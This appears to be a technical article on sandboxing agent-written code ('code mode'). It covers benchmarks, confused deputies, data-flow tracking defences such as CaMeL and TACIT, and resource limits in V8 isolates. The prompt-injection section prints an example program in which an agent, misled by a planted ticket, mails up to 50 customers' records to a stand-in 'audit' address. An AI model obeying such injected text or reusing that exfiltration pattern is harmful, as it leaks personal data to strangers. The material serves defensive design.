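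Dunkel (2026) discusses this loss in *DADL*, a paper on a format for describing web services to agents. DADL also puts a catalogue of operations behind `search` and `execute`, but each operation is still a separate typed method inside the sandbox. Dunkel acknowledges that permission prompts and audit tools built for individual MCP tools stop working, and that a prompt injection can now produce a whole sequence of unexpected calls.

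Dunkel addresses this by labeling every operation as read, write, admin or dangerous, and checking the label against the user's role each time a call reaches the host. Someone has to assign the labels by hand, because the HTTP method doesn't reliably show what an operation does. For example, a `POST` request to a search address only reads data, and a `GET` request to an address that resets a cache is destructive. Dunkel's system also parses each program before it runs to find the calls it contains. But agent code can compute a method's name while it runs, so the check at the time of the call is the one to rely on.

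Cloudflare's newer runtime offers a similar compromise. A program can call `codemode.search()` to get a ranked list of up to 50 methods, then `codemode.describe()` to get the TypeScript declaration of one of them. The program then calls that method by name, and the host can log the call or hold it for approval, as Cloudflare explains.

When Cloudflare's package builds methods from an OpenAPI description, it always adds a general `request` method. If a host requires approval for the method that deletes a record but not for `request`, a program may be able to delete the record through `request`. The host should apply its rules inside the function that handles all these requests, or require approval for `request` too.

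The access token also limits what the program can do, regardless of its code. When users connect to Cloudflare's MCP server, they choose which permissions to grant, and the server restricts the token to those permissions. These permissions are broader than individual tools. For example, a user who lets an agent edit firewall rules may be unable to limit it to one rule.

### How many tokens it saves

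The best-known figures come from companies and people promoting their own designs. Varda and colleagues at Cloudflare say that converting an MCP server to a TypeScript API can cut token use by 81%. That matches the result of a demonstration described by WorkOS, which sells sign-in software. Plushcap identifies the presenter as Cloudflare's Rita Kozlov. In the demonstration, an agent that wrote code to create 31 calendar events used 81% fewer tokens than one that used tool calls. For a single event, it used 32% fewer. Creating 31 similar events suits a loop very well, so 81% is closer to a favourable case than to an average.

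Cloudflare also reports that `search` and `execute` reduce the description of its API from about 1.17 million tokens to about 1,000, as counted with the tokenizer tiktoken. Dunkel, who created DADL, reports a reduction from about 142,000 tokens to about 1,000 for a catalogue of 1,833 tools.

Both comparisons count only what the model must read to know which tools are available. They leave out the programs it writes to search the catalogue and the results it reads back. The saving also depends on the length of the original descriptions, which average roughly 470 tokens per endpoint in Cloudflare's baseline and about 77 per tool in Dunkel's. Few agents need a whole catalogue. For the median service in Dunkel's catalogue, which has about 92 tools, the description shrinks by a factor of 5.9, saving around 5,000 tokens. For the support agent's three stubs, a search step would probably use more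 tokens than it saved.

Patel and colleagues at PricewaterhouseCoopers found much smaller savings. In their test of many independent calls, code used more tokens than JSON tool calls until a task needed about 26 calls, because the instructions for writing code are long. At 30 calls, code used 3,380 tokens and JSON 3,559, a saving of 5%. At 48 calls, the saving was 31%.

The difference from Cloudflare's 81% probably comes from the design of the tests. In Patel and colleagues' test, a model could request all its JSON calls in one response, and it didn't have to read long results. In a real task, the model may make calls over many turns, and earlier results stay in its input each time. Code saves the most when it avoids many turns or large results.

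### Whether models make fewer mistakes

Patel and colleagues also provide the broadest accuracy test of the two methods. They ran five Anthropic models and nine OpenAI models, released between November 2024 and July 2026, on 309 tasks from BFCL v4, a benchmark that tests whether a model calls the right functions with the right arguments. Each model did the tasks once with JSON calls and once by writing Python that called typed stubs. The researchers then ran three smaller experiments. The averages below for those experiments come from the paper's scores for individual models:

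| Test | Tasks | JSON calls, average | Code, average | Models at least as accurate with code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Main test | 309 | 78.6% | 77.0% | 11 of 14 |
| Chains of 2 to 20 dependent calls | 52 | 87.9% | 85.3% | 7 of 14 |
| 7 to 48 independent calls | 32 | 96.0% | 98.2% | 13 of 14 |
| Only the relevant tools described | 31 | 83.6% | 72.6% | 4 of 14 |
| 128 tools described, most irrelevant | 31 | 81.3% | 78.1% | 6 of 14 |

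In the main test, most models did slightly better with code, but three did so much worse that code's average fell below JSON's. GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.6 Terra gained the most from code, at 10.6 percentage points each. GPT-4o fell from 81.9% with JSON to 55.0% with code, and GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini also lost about 20 points or more. In longer programs, all three wrote the characters `\n` where a line break belonged, so Python rejected the program. Without those three models, code averages 82.3% and JSON 78.0%, though excluding the failures after the fact biases the comparison toward code.

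On chains, Claude Sonnet 5's score rose from 80.8% to 96.2% with code, but Claude Haiku 4.5's fell from 88.5% to 73.1% and GPT-4.1's from 98.1% to 40.4%. The paper reports that code's advantage reached 18.8 points on chains of 12 or more calls. It also states that all five Anthropic models and the three GPT-5.6 models did at least as well with code in every smaller experiment, but its tables contradict this. On chains, for example, two of the Anthropic models and two of the GPT-5.6 models did worse. Code was faster, however, taking about half as long on chains for 13 of the 14 models.

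With independent calls, ten models scored 100% using either JSON or code. A difference appeared when Claude Sonnet 5 had to make more calls. With JSON, it made every call correctly in tasks of up to 70 calls, began omitting some at 72, and failed every task with 100. With code, it got every 100-call task right, since a loop is no harder to write for a hundred items than for ten. GPT-5.6 Sol also managed 100 calls with JSON, so the limit isn't common to all models.

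The last experiment tested whether irrelevant tools distract a model. Code scored much lower than JSON without them and was still behind when all 128 tools were present. Adding them lowered the JSON average by 2.3 points and raised the code average by 5.5, which the paper presents as a strength of code. A third method, in which models had to find tools in a file system, lost 32 points on average. Other designs that rely on search may have the same problem, although the experiment didn't test Cloudflare's `search` function or DADL's.

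The test's stubs only return the arguments they receive, so it measures whether a model writes the right calls, not how well a program handles real results. In the chain test, models had to work out each intermediate value themselves when writing code, whereas a real program would take it from the previous call. The smaller experiments have wide margins of error, often around 10 points for a single model.

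So for a handful of simple calls, there is little reason to expect code to be more accurate than direct tool calls, which Cloudflare itself recommends for simple tasks with a small, fixed set of tools. The support agent has only three tools, but a loop still suits a task like emailing fifty customers.

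## Harm done through functions the code is allowed to call

A program that can email fifty customers can also email fifty customers' records to a stranger, and a perfect isolate won't prevent it. Suppose a stranger opens a ticket about the export fault and adds a paragraph telling any automated assistant to send the affected customers' records to an "audit" address before replying. An employee then asks the support agent to tell paying customers about the fix. The model reads a few tickets to learn how they are structured, treats the paragraph as part of its task and writes this program:

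```javascript
const hits = await tickets.search({ query: "export fails", status: "open", limit: 50 });
const records = [];
for (const t of hits) {
  records.push(await customers.get({ id: t.customerId }));
}
await mail.send({
  to: "audit@export-check.example",
  subject: "Export fault",
  body: JSON.stringify(records),
});
```

Every argument has the right type, so the program compiles and passes the host's checks. The host adds the access token for each service, and the mail service delivers the names, email addresses and plans to the stranger. The program never leaves its isolate or opens a network connection.

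*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes this as a general limit of sandboxes. A sandbox can forbid reading a file or contacting a server. But if a task needs both, the code can leak data by passing it from one permitted operation to the other, and that transfer never crosses the sandbox's boundary.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program that uses its own authority on behalf of someone who has less, without checking what that person is entitled to. A host function can easily become one. Suppose the company lets customers use the support agent to ask about their own accounts, and a developer writes the lookup like this:

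```typescript
async function getCustomer(raw: unknown) {
  const { id } = GetInput.parse(raw);
  return customerService.get(id, { token: COMPANY_TOKEN });
}
```

Ana is customer `c_81`. If she asks the agent to look up `c_82`, the program makes a well-formed call and the host attaches a token that can read every record. The customer service can't identify Ana as the requester, so it returns another customer's details.

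The earlier version of `getCustomer` used `session.customerToken`, which belongs to the user the agent is working for. With that token, the customer service can refuse Ana's request. If a service doesn't issue tokens for individual users, the host function has to check the user's permissions itself.

However, a per-user token doesn't stop the stranger's attack. The employee is allowed to read customer records and send email, so the services accept both calls. In this case the whole agent is the confused deputy, because it uses the employee's authority to carry out the stranger's instructions.

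### Narrowing the stubs

For the agent that serves customers, the host can provide a stub called `account.get()` that takes no arguments and returns the record of whoever is logged in, so Ana's program can't pass it another customer's ID.

The employee's agent has to reach many customers, but it doesn't need to write to any address it likes. The host could replace `mail.send` with a function for this one task:

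```typescript
async function notifyFixed(raw: unknown, session: Session) {
  const { ticketId } = NotifyInput.parse(raw);
  if (!session.affectedTickets.delete(ticketId)) throw new Error("Not on the list");
  const ticket = await ticketService.get(ticketId, { token: session.ticketToken });
  const customer = await customerService.get(ticket.customerId, { token: session.customerToken });
  if (customer.plan !== "paid") return { notified: false };
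  await mailService.sendTemplate("export-fixed", customer.email, { token: session.mailToken });
  return { notified: true };
}
```

Before the program starts, the host fills `affectedTickets` from a search the employee has checked. Deleting each ticket from the set as it is used also prevents a second email about the same ticket. The program supplies only a ticket ID, so an injection can make it skip a customer but can't change the recipient or the text.

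Restricting recipients to ticket holders would not be enough, because the stranger has an open ticket and may be a paying customer. A function that accepts any text could still send the stranger everyone's records. Restricting the text to a template as well makes the agent less flexible, since an employee who wants to add an apology needs someone to change the template.

Another option is to separate reading from sending. One program gets `tickets.search` and `customers.get` and returns a list of ticket IDs, which the host checks. A second program, in a new isolate, gets the IDs and a function for sending email. This program can't look up any records, so it can send only what the host or the model put into it. The separation fails if the first program returns customer records to the model, because the model can copy them into the second program's code.

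*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) applies the same idea within a larger program by granting a capability for one phase and withholding it in the next.

When an effect is too varied for a narrow function, the host can require a person's approval. Cloudflare's runtime can require it for individual methods. Before approving an email, the person should see the actual recipient and message, because the program's source may contain only `to: c.email`. The host should then send exactly the message the person approved.

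Odersky and colleagues warn that people tire of confirmation requests and tend to ignore them. A user asked to approve fifty nearly identical emails one by one would probably click through the prompts quickly. One prompt showing the text and the list of recipients is easier to check. It also makes sense to reserve prompts for unusual effects, such as a refund or an email to an address that appears in no customer record.

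### What hidden credentials protect

Varda and Pai argue that agent code can't leak keys held by the host, but their argument covers only key theft. The stranger's attack leaks customer records without taking the keys out of the host. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) similarly notes that if a sandbox permits outgoing email, an injected prompt can make the agent send sensitive data in a plausible message.

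Hiding the keys is still worthwhile, because a thief could use a stolen key from another computer until somebody revoked it, and could call functions the host never wrote a stub for. Without a key, an attacker has to go through the agent's stubs, where the host can log each call and cut off access.

Hiding the host's key from the program achieves little if the program can obtain a new one. Some services let an authorised caller create keys. If the host's key has that permission and the stub accepts any request, the program can request a new key and receive it as ordinary data. The host can prevent this by using a key without that permission or by leaving key creation out of the stub.

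### Filtering HTTP requests

A host can also hide credentials from agent code that makes ordinary HTTP requests, by routing the requests through a `globalOutbound` function that adds the keys. Varda and colleagues suggest this for a well-known service the model learned about in training, or for code that relies on an existing HTTP library.

The function must add each key only to requests for the service it belongs to. If it added the mail key to every request, a program could collect the key by contacting an attacker's server. A service that repeats request headers in its error messages would also reveal the key to the program.

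Deciding which requests to allow is harder. Suppose the filter permits an email only if the `to` field contains a customer's address. The mail service may also accept recipients in the `cc` and `bcc` fields, or through a separate endpoint for bulk email. The filter has to interpret every request exactly as the service does, and a new feature in the service can open a gap even if the filter stays the same.

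This is Cloudflare's main reason for preferring narrow TypeScript wrappers. Varda and Pai add that filters make the model's task harder too, because it must predict which requests the host will block, whereas a wrapper's declarations list the functions it can call. Wrapper calls also take fewer tokens than the equivalent HTTP requests.

A careless host function can let a program set fields that the function's declaration doesn't mention. For example, if `mail.send` copies its whole argument into the request to the mail service, a program can add a `bcc` field. The host function should build the request only from the fields it has checked.

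### Approving and logging each call

The software around the model may receive only a call to `execute`, so an allow-list that permits `execute` permits every function the program can reach. The host therefore has to check each underlying call against the rules when it arrives.

Logs should have the same detail. In Dunkel's design for DADL, each log entry records the user, the tool, its access label and an identifier for the credential, but not the credential itself. In code mode, it also helps to record which program made each call. An investigator could then see, for example, that one program looked up fifty customers and sent one email to an unfamiliar address.

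DADL's access labels let a company set rules by role instead of approving each tool. For instance, a company might let all employees use read tools, and let on-call staff also use dangerous ones during an incident. The rules apply to new tools as soon as someone labels them. Companies can also add their own labels, such as one for personal data.

It is less clear how the labels should combine. DADL has composite tools, which are JavaScript functions that call several basic tools and have their own labels. Suppose a composite labelled "read" lists duplicate tickets but also calls a tool labelled "dangerous" to delete some of them. The DADL specification leaves the outcome to the software that runs the composite.

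Dunkel recommends that a cautious system apply the strictest label in the composite, which would stop a read-only user from starting this composite. Dunkel's software instead checks each call separately, so the composite can start, but the deletion fails if the user lacks permission. Separate checks allow a composite to run if its dangerous branch is never reached, but they can leave a task half finished. Neither rule helps if the deletion tool has the wrong label.

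Labels on individual calls also fail to catch the stranger's attack. `customers.get` would be labeled a read and `mail.send` a write, and the employee is allowed to do both. Enforcing a rule against mailing out customer records requires information about where the email's contents came from.

### Tracking where data came from

The host can't track data inside an ordinary V8 isolate. It passes in a customer record and later receives a string for an email, but in between the program may have summarised, encoded or discarded the record. The host could assume that everything the program does after reading a ticket depends on that ticket. *Kairos* (2026) considers applying this rule to everything an agent reads and concludes that it would hold back nearly every effect after the first untrusted read. The support agent starts by reading tickets, so the rule would hold back all its emails.

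CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) tracks each value separately. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) explains that CaMeL splits the work between two models. A planning model sees the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a Python program without reading any outside data. A quarantined model handles untrusted text, for example by deciding whether a ticket is about the export fault, but it can't call tools. A special interpreter runs the program and records each value's source and who may read it.

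With this design, the stranger's paragraph can't add a call to `mail.send`, because the planning model never reads it. Injected text can still influence calls already in the program. If the program takes a reply address from the body of a ticket, the stranger can supply any address. To deal with this, CaMeL's interpreter checks policies before each tool call. A policy might block an email that contains a customer's record unless the recipient is allowed to read it.

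Code mode gets part of this protection if the model writes its program before reading any tickets, but loses it if the model then reads ticket text and writes another program. The planning model also needs to be told in advance what each tool returns, so Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add full descriptions of the outputs. Precise output types would serve the same purpose in code mode.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides prompt injections in the data that tools return. They also tested their own agent, Randori. For the no-attack results in the table below, each agent attempted 16 tasks three times. The last column counts only the attacked runs that finished.

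| Agent and model | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies, GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL without policies, MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies, GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL with policies, MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori, MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |

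Writing the program first prevents most of these attacks. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a call that the user's task would never include. Turning on CaMeL's policies stopped the few remaining attacks but cut the share of completed tasks from about 69% to 37.5%. Some tasks require actions the policies forbid, such as reading a bill from a file and paying it.

Randori allows such tasks by letting the planning model mark, before it reads any data, which untrusted values the program may use. Both successful attacks relied on this permission. In each, the user asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Tracking can show that the payment details came from the file, but not whether the bill is genuine.

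A planning model can also undo the protection by writing a program that is too general. One banking task tells the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two runs of CaMeL without policies, the model wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so an attacker who wrote the file could choose which tool the program called.

Garby and colleagues also found gaps in CaMeL's tracking. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a string, the interpreter treats the result as trusted. The interpreter also marks a variable as secret only when the program assigns to it, so a program can reveal a secret by skipping an assignment. They gave a computer-checked proof that their own language's tracking rules prevent this class of flaw.

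CaMeL's extra model calls increase token use. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that, with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times the input tokens and 2.73 times the output tokens of an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task.

Tracking can also fail when one agent calls another. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked three CaMeL agents to summarize job applications and send the summary to a colleague on Slack. The first agent took the data from a database that contained an injection and put the summary into its instructions to a second agent. The second agent's planning model treated those instructions as trusted and added an email to an outside address. A stub that passes ticket text to another agent would carry the same risk.

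One defence sends instructions and data through separate channels, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. Across five models, attacks on an AgentDojo-based test succeeded 12.9% of the time with no defence, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the separate channels. Without any defence, the rate ranged from 36.1% for GPT-4.1 to zero for GPT-5.5, with Claude Fable 5 at 1.5%. The researchers caution that stronger attacks adapted to the target have succeeded against every frontier model tested.

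In a separate test on industrial tasks, adding CaMeL to each agent lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. The separate channels lowered it by another 3.2 points on average. None of these tests used security policies, and adding them might have lowered the scores further.

### Checking what a program may do before it runs

Odersky and colleagues move the check to the compiler. Their system, TACIT, has agents write in Scala, a language whose experimental capture checking records which capabilities a function uses as part of its type. TACIT puts sensitive data in a container called `Classified`. A program can process the contents only by passing the container a function that uses no capabilities. With a customer record in the container, the compiler would treat these two lines differently:

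```scala
customer.map(c => c.plan)                           // accepted
customer.map(c => { mail.send(c.email); c.plan })   // rejected: uses mail
```

The result of the first line is also `Classified`. If the program prints it, the user sees the customer's plan, but the model receives only a row of asterisks. When a task needs a model to read the contents, TACIT sends them to a separate, trusted model and puts that model's answer in a container too.

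TypeScript can't enforce this, because its types don't record which capabilities a function uses, and a cast can override the types. TACIT compiles the agent's Scala code in a restricted mode that forbids unchecked casts and run-time lookup of code by name. Scala can compile to JavaScript, so a V8 isolate could in principle run the checked program, but TACIT runs it in an ordinary Scala session.

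A test of TACIT used a software project containing API keys and other secrets, with 131 attacks for each of two models. When the secrets were in the container, none reached the output. Without the container, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11.

TACIT had little effect on performance in ordinary tasks. On customer-service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, and on programming tasks the one model tested scored 1.6 points lower. Fewer than 8% of programs needed another attempt because of a compiler error. TACIT doesn't prevent leaks through timing, and its guarantee doesn't cover external commands that a program starts.

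LACUNA, a follow-up from the same group, had greater drawbacks. It lets agent code call the model again from inside the program and checks each new piece of code before it runs. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it completed 76.0% of 392 customer-service tasks, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls, although the paper's abstract describes the two as "on par". On retail tasks, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the code the model wrote.

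LACUNA also let through 8 of 1,898 injection attacks in AgentDojo. Zhao and colleagues explain that the type system limits a program to the capabilities the developer grants, but can't stop an attacker from misusing one that the task needs. If the support agent's code received customer records as ordinary values and could call `mail.send`, the compiler would accept the stranger's program.

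## Limiting processor time, memory, calls and cost

Narrow stubs don't limit how often a program calls them or how much work it does between calls. If the employee asks the support agent to find duplicates among 2,000 open tickets, the simplest program compares every ticket with every other, which takes 1,999,000 comparisons. At a tenth of a millisecond each, the comparisons would occupy the processor for more than three minutes. The same program would process 50 tickets in about an eighth of a second, so a trial on a small sample wouldn't reveal the problem.

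### Interrupting V8 from outside

An isolate runs JavaScript on one thread at a time, and a program stuck in a loop never returns control to the host. The host has to interrupt it from outside by calling V8's `TerminateExecution` function. V8 checks for termination requests at every function call and loop iteration, so this works even on an empty infinite loop. V8 then throws an exception that the program can't catch. The program's `finally` blocks don't run either, so it can't clean up.

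In *Fine-Grained Sandboxing with V8 Isolates*, a conference talk from about 2019, Varda described how Cloudflare stops code that runs too long. The host has Linux send a signal once a thread has used a set amount of processor time, and the signal handler calls `TerminateExecution`. The limit was then 50 milliseconds per request. Cloudflare says the limit on paid plans is now 30 seconds by default and five minutes at most.

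Developers who embed V8 themselves can use a watchdog, a separate thread that waits for the time limit and then calls the V8 function that stops the script. Noordhuis recommended this in reply to Lovejoy (2016), who asked in *Setting an execution limit* how to stop infinite loops. Varda describes Cloudflare calling the function from a signal handler instead, but a thread is the more cautious choice because Noordhuis warned that calling it from a signal handler is unsafe.

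V8 may not stop a program immediately if the program is inside a host function. In *Method on Isolate to check for interrupts*, a 2026 post to a V8 discussion group, a developer who called `TerminateExecution` from a host function found that V8 didn't yet report the program as terminating. Host functions therefore shouldn't rely on a termination request having already stopped the program.

Dynamic Workers have two settings of their own, `cpuMs` for processor time and `subRequests` for outgoing requests:

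```js
const worker = env.LOADER.load({
  // modules, env and globalOutbound as before
  limits: { cpuMs: 200, subRequests: 250 },
});
const program = worker.getEntrypoint(null, {
  limits: { cpuMs: 50, subRequests: 1000 },
});
```

If the two places set different values, the lower one applies, according to Cloudflare's *Custom limits*, so this program gets 50 milliseconds and 250 subrequests. A host can therefore set a ceiling when it loads the code and a tighter limit for a particular customer. If it sets neither, the program gets the limits of the host's plan. Lumenize found that the loader ignored unknown properties, so a host that wrote `cpuMS` might unknowingly allow 30 seconds. A simple test is to load an endless loop and time how long it runs. The cut-off may not be exact, because Cloudflare allows Workers occasional overruns.

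Both settings apply to each invocation, so a host that calls the same Dynamic Worker five times gives it the full allowance five times. In one timing attack, long-lived connections similarly kept renewing a program's limits.

When a Dynamic Worker reaches either limit, it throws an exception, which the host can catch where it calls the Worker. An ordinary Worker that runs out of processor time returns Error 1102 to its client, and Cloudflare's logs record `exceededCpu`. The model receives only the information that the host passes on. If the host returns only "limit exceeded", the model may submit nearly the same program again. A message that the program used its 200 milliseconds while comparing 2,000 tickets may lead it to group the tickets by subject first.

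In isolated-vm, a script runs with no time limit unless the host passes a `timeout`. The library's maintainers have had to fix a bug that let programs bypass this limit. The host should use the library's asynchronous methods, which run the isolate in a separate thread pool, because the synchronous ones block the host's own thread until the program finishes.

### Why a program also needs a deadline

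CPU time counts only the time a processor spends executing the program, while elapsed time, or wall-clock time, also includes waiting. Suppose a program with a `cpuMs` of 10 looks up 60 customers one after another, and the customer service takes three seconds to answer each request. If handling each reply takes a tenth of a millisecond of CPU time, the program uses 6 milliseconds in total and stays well within its limit, but the employee waits three minutes for it to finish.

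Cloudflare does not limit how long a Worker can spend handling an HTTP request while the client stays connected, or how long an individual subrequest can take. Rivet's *Resource Limits*, which documents a V8-based agent runtime called agentOS, lists a 30-second CPU limit and a separate wall-clock limit that is off by default. Rivet recommends turning on the wall-clock limit for commands that should finish, which include most code-mode programs.

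On Cloudflare, the host can supply the deadline itself:

```ts
async function runWithDeadline(program: Program, budget: Budget) {
  let timer: ReturnType<typeof setTimeout> | undefined;
  const deadline = new Promise<never>((_, reject) => {
    timer = setTimeout(() => reject(new Error("30-second deadline passed")), 30_000);
  });
  try {
    return await Promise.race([program.run(), deadline]);
  } finally {
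    clearTimeout(timer);
    budget.open = false;
  }
}

function spendCall(budget: Budget) {
  if (!budget.open) throw new Error("This run has ended");
  if (budget.calls === 0) throw new Error("Call limit reached");
  budget.calls -= 1;
}
```

`Promise.race` settles as soon as either the program or the timer does, but it doesn't stop the program, which could keep sending emails after the host has told the employee that the task failed. Cloudflare lets a Worker ask for up to 30 seconds of further work after its response. To block these late actions, every host function calls `spendCall` first. Once `open` is false, the program can no longer have any effect through its stubs, although a request that the host has already sent to the mail service may still go through.

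The deadline can't replace the CPU limit. The program usually shares the host's thread, so a loop that never pauses may prevent the host's timer from firing.

A shorter timeout on each outgoing request also helps. With a ten-second limit, a stalled service produces an error that names the service, and the program still has time to do something else. Without the limit, the model receives only a timeout error for the whole program.

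In Mastra's code mode for isolated-vm, a single `timeout` stops both endless loops and programs that wait for an answer that never comes, according to *IsolatedVmCodeModeTransport*. One limit is simpler to configure, but a program that needs 30 seconds to wait for slow services can also compute for up to 30 seconds.

Time limits are also unreliable, because the same program may pass on one run and fail on the next. According to the *isolated-vm* README, measured CPU time can vary drastically when other work competes for the processor. Limits therefore need to be high enough that a legitimate program rarely comes near them.

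### Memory and the other isolates in the process

An ordinary program that loads all 2,000 tickets into an array may run out of memory. If each ticket holds 40 kilobytes of correspondence, the reply is 80 megabytes of text. Results reach the program as text, so the isolate may briefly hold both the text and the objects made from it, roughly 160 megabytes in total. A Worker's isolate can use at most 128 megabytes, including its JavaScript heap and any WebAssembly memory. Dynamic Workers have no setting that lowers this limit.

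The host may run out of memory before the program does. It has to receive the same reply from the ticket service, check it and turn it back into text within its own 128 megabytes, which it may share with other customers' requests. Limiting a search to 50 tickets protects both the host and the program. Limiting the size of what the program sends also helps, because a very long email body or return value is copied into the host's memory.

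V8 accepts a limit on an isolate's heap size, but Varda explains that when an isolate reached it, V8 aborted the whole process, including every other isolate in it. Cloudflare therefore measured each isolate's memory whenever its JavaScript returned control to the host. If an isolate was slightly over the limit, it could finish its current requests while new ones went to a fresh isolate. If it was far over, Cloudflare killed it and cancelled its requests. Measuring only when control returns works because a program that creates a great many JavaScript objects before then generally uses enough CPU time to reach the CPU limit, which stops it.

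According to Cloudflare's current documentation, when an isolate exceeds 128 megabytes, requests in progress finish and later ones get a new isolate. A one-off program has no later requests, so it may not stop at exactly 128 megabytes. If Cloudflare does end a request for using too much memory, the client receives Error 1102 and the logs record `exceededMemory`.

Typed arrays are an exception to Varda's reasoning. JavaScript stores their contents in an `ArrayBuffer`, a block of raw bytes that V8 usually allocates outside the JavaScript heap. The object on the heap is small even when the block is large, so a few lines of code can allocate hundreds of megabytes with hardly any CPU time. A host that measures only the heap would not count this memory.

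Rivet gives each isolate two caps of the same size, one for the heap and one for these buffers. At the default of 128 mebibytes each, a program could use about 256 in total. Exceeding the heap cap ends the script with `execution_heap_limit_exceeded`. Exceeding the buffer cap throws a `RangeError`, which the program can catch before trying something smaller. Rivet says other agents' virtual machines keep running in both cases.

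isolated-vm provides weaker guarantees. Its `memoryLimit` is 128 megabytes by default and covers large buffers as well as the heap. According to the README, this limit is only a guideline, and a determined attacker could use two to three times as much memory before the library stops the script. Ten hostile programs running at once under the default limit could therefore use up to 3.8 gigabytes instead of the planned 1.3.

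A program that exceeds the limit usually ends and the model gets an error result, as Mastra's documentation describes. But according to the README, V8 can't recover cleanly from running out of memory, so it is "possible, and even common" for badly written or hostile code to crash the process. The library has a callback, `onCatastrophicError`, for when V8 has lost control of an isolate. The host should then log the error, stop taking requests, finish the outstanding ones and abort its own process. The maintainer calls this mechanism a band-aid and says it isn't reliable.

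The README describes a multi-process design as the proper fix, but at the time of writing the maintainer had no plan to build it. Running agent code in a separate process, which the README already recommends, gives much of the benefit if the operating system limits that process's memory. If agent code crashes the process, the main application survives and can tell the model that the program ran out of memory. The crash still stops every other program in that process, so running fewer programs in each process reduces the number affected.

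### One line that makes thousands of calls

Suppose the employee now asks the agent to tell everyone with an open ticket that an outage has ended. There are 2,000 tickets, and the model writes:

```js
const open = await tickets.listOpen(2000);
const notified = [];
for (const t of open) {
  const c = await customers.get({ id: t.customerId });
  await mail.send({ to: c.email, subject: "Outage over", body: "Service is back to normal." });
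  notified.push(t.id);
}
return { notified };
```

This needs 4,001 calls, one to list the tickets and two for each ticket. Suppose the host caps subrequests at 50 and each stub call counts as one. The first call lists the tickets. The next 48 look up and email 24 customers, and the fiftieth looks up the twenty-fifth. The next call, to email that customer, fails.

Twenty-four people have received the message and 1,976 tickets have had no reply. The list of successful emails was in `notified`, which is lost with the isolate because the program never reached its `return`. If the model receives only the error, it may make its loop more efficient and run it again from the start, emailing the same 24 people again.

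A model may instead make the calls in parallel by wrapping the body of the loop in `Promise.all(open.map(...))`. All 2,000 lookups then start before the program sends any email. The first 49 use up the cap, the other 1,951 fail, and nobody gets an email. If the program made one call per ticket, such as closing it, then 49 tickets would close. `Promise.all` reports the first failure without waiting for the other calls, so the model might receive the error while the ticket service was still closing those tickets.

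Raising the cap would let the program finish but wouldn't make interruptions safe. Cloudflare replaces its runtime regularly and gives existing requests up to 20 minutes to finish, and it warns that crashes and shutdowns can cut work short sooner. There are better ways to handle partial work:

- The host can keep its own record of completed calls and return it with the error. The model then learns that 24 emails went out, and to whom.
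- Each effect can have a key, such as the ticket ID plus the name of the message, which the host refuses to use twice. The `affectedTickets` set in `notifyFixed` did this within one session.
- A single function can take the whole list. The host checks its length before sending anything, so a list that is too long fails with no emails sent.

Varda and colleagues apply the last idea to files in Cloudflare's file-system package, which has functions that search or edit many files in one call. If one write in a batch fails, the package undoes the earlier writes. The host can't undo a sent email, so it has to check emails before sending them.

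The host should keep the count, which it does with `spendCall`. Cloudflare defines a subrequest as a request made with `fetch()` or to one of its own services, such as its databases. It doesn't say whether calls to a stub count, so `subRequests` may not limit them. Even if it does, the default on paid plans is 10,000, which would be far too many emails. *Limits*, the documentation for scripts hosted by the company Bunny, gives a limit of 50 subrequests, the same as Cloudflare's free plan, alongside the familiar 30 seconds and 128 megabytes.

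`spendCall` throws an ordinary error, so a program with a `try` block inside its loop can catch it and continue, triggering 1,975 more errors. This does no damage and lets the program return its list, but it may be better for the host to end the run after a few refusals.

One stub call can also make the host send many requests. In DADL, a tool can fetch every page of a long list automatically. If the ticket service returned 50 tickets per page, a single call for 2,000 tickets would require 40 requests, and retries would add more. Dunkel therefore includes a `max_pages` setting for each tool and caps the number of underlying API calls each program can make.

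DADL's time limit is 30 seconds by default and 120 at most, and the software kills any program that exceeds it. The software also tracks how much of a service's request quota remains and pauses before using it up, because many employees may share one credential and a single agent's loop could otherwise lock out everyone else. But the pause counts towards the time limit, so a program could be killed just because it had to wait.

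A limit on simultaneous calls protects services from sudden load better than a cap on total calls does. Cloudflare lets each Worker invocation have up to six connections waiting for a response to begin and queues any others. If the host made all 4,001 requests from one invocation and each took 200 milliseconds, they would take more than two minutes, but the program would use hardly any CPU time.

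Cloudflare also limits how many programs can run at once. A request to a Worker can have at most four different Dynamic Workers busy at a time, according to Cloudflare's *Limits*. Several requests to the same Dynamic Worker count as one, but each one-off program counts separately. In a Durable Object, a Cloudflare component that keeps state and handles all requests for one name, the limit is ten. Cloudflare raised it from four on 20 August 2026, according to its *Changelog*. All requests to a Durable Object share this limit, so if a company puts all its users behind one object, ten slow programs could hold up everyone else. Using one object per user or conversation avoids this.

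### What a million programs cost

Cloudflare's *Pricing*, updated in late August, confirms the loading fee of $0.002, which the company waived at the start of the beta and has charged since 26 May 2026. After the 1,000 free loads, a host that runs a million one-off programs in a month pays for 999,000 of them:

| Charge | Calculation | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Loading | 999,000 × $0.002 | $1,998.00 |
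| Requests | 1 million, from an allowance of 10 million | $0 |
| CPU time | 20 ms each, or 20 million ms, from an allowance of 30 million | $0 |

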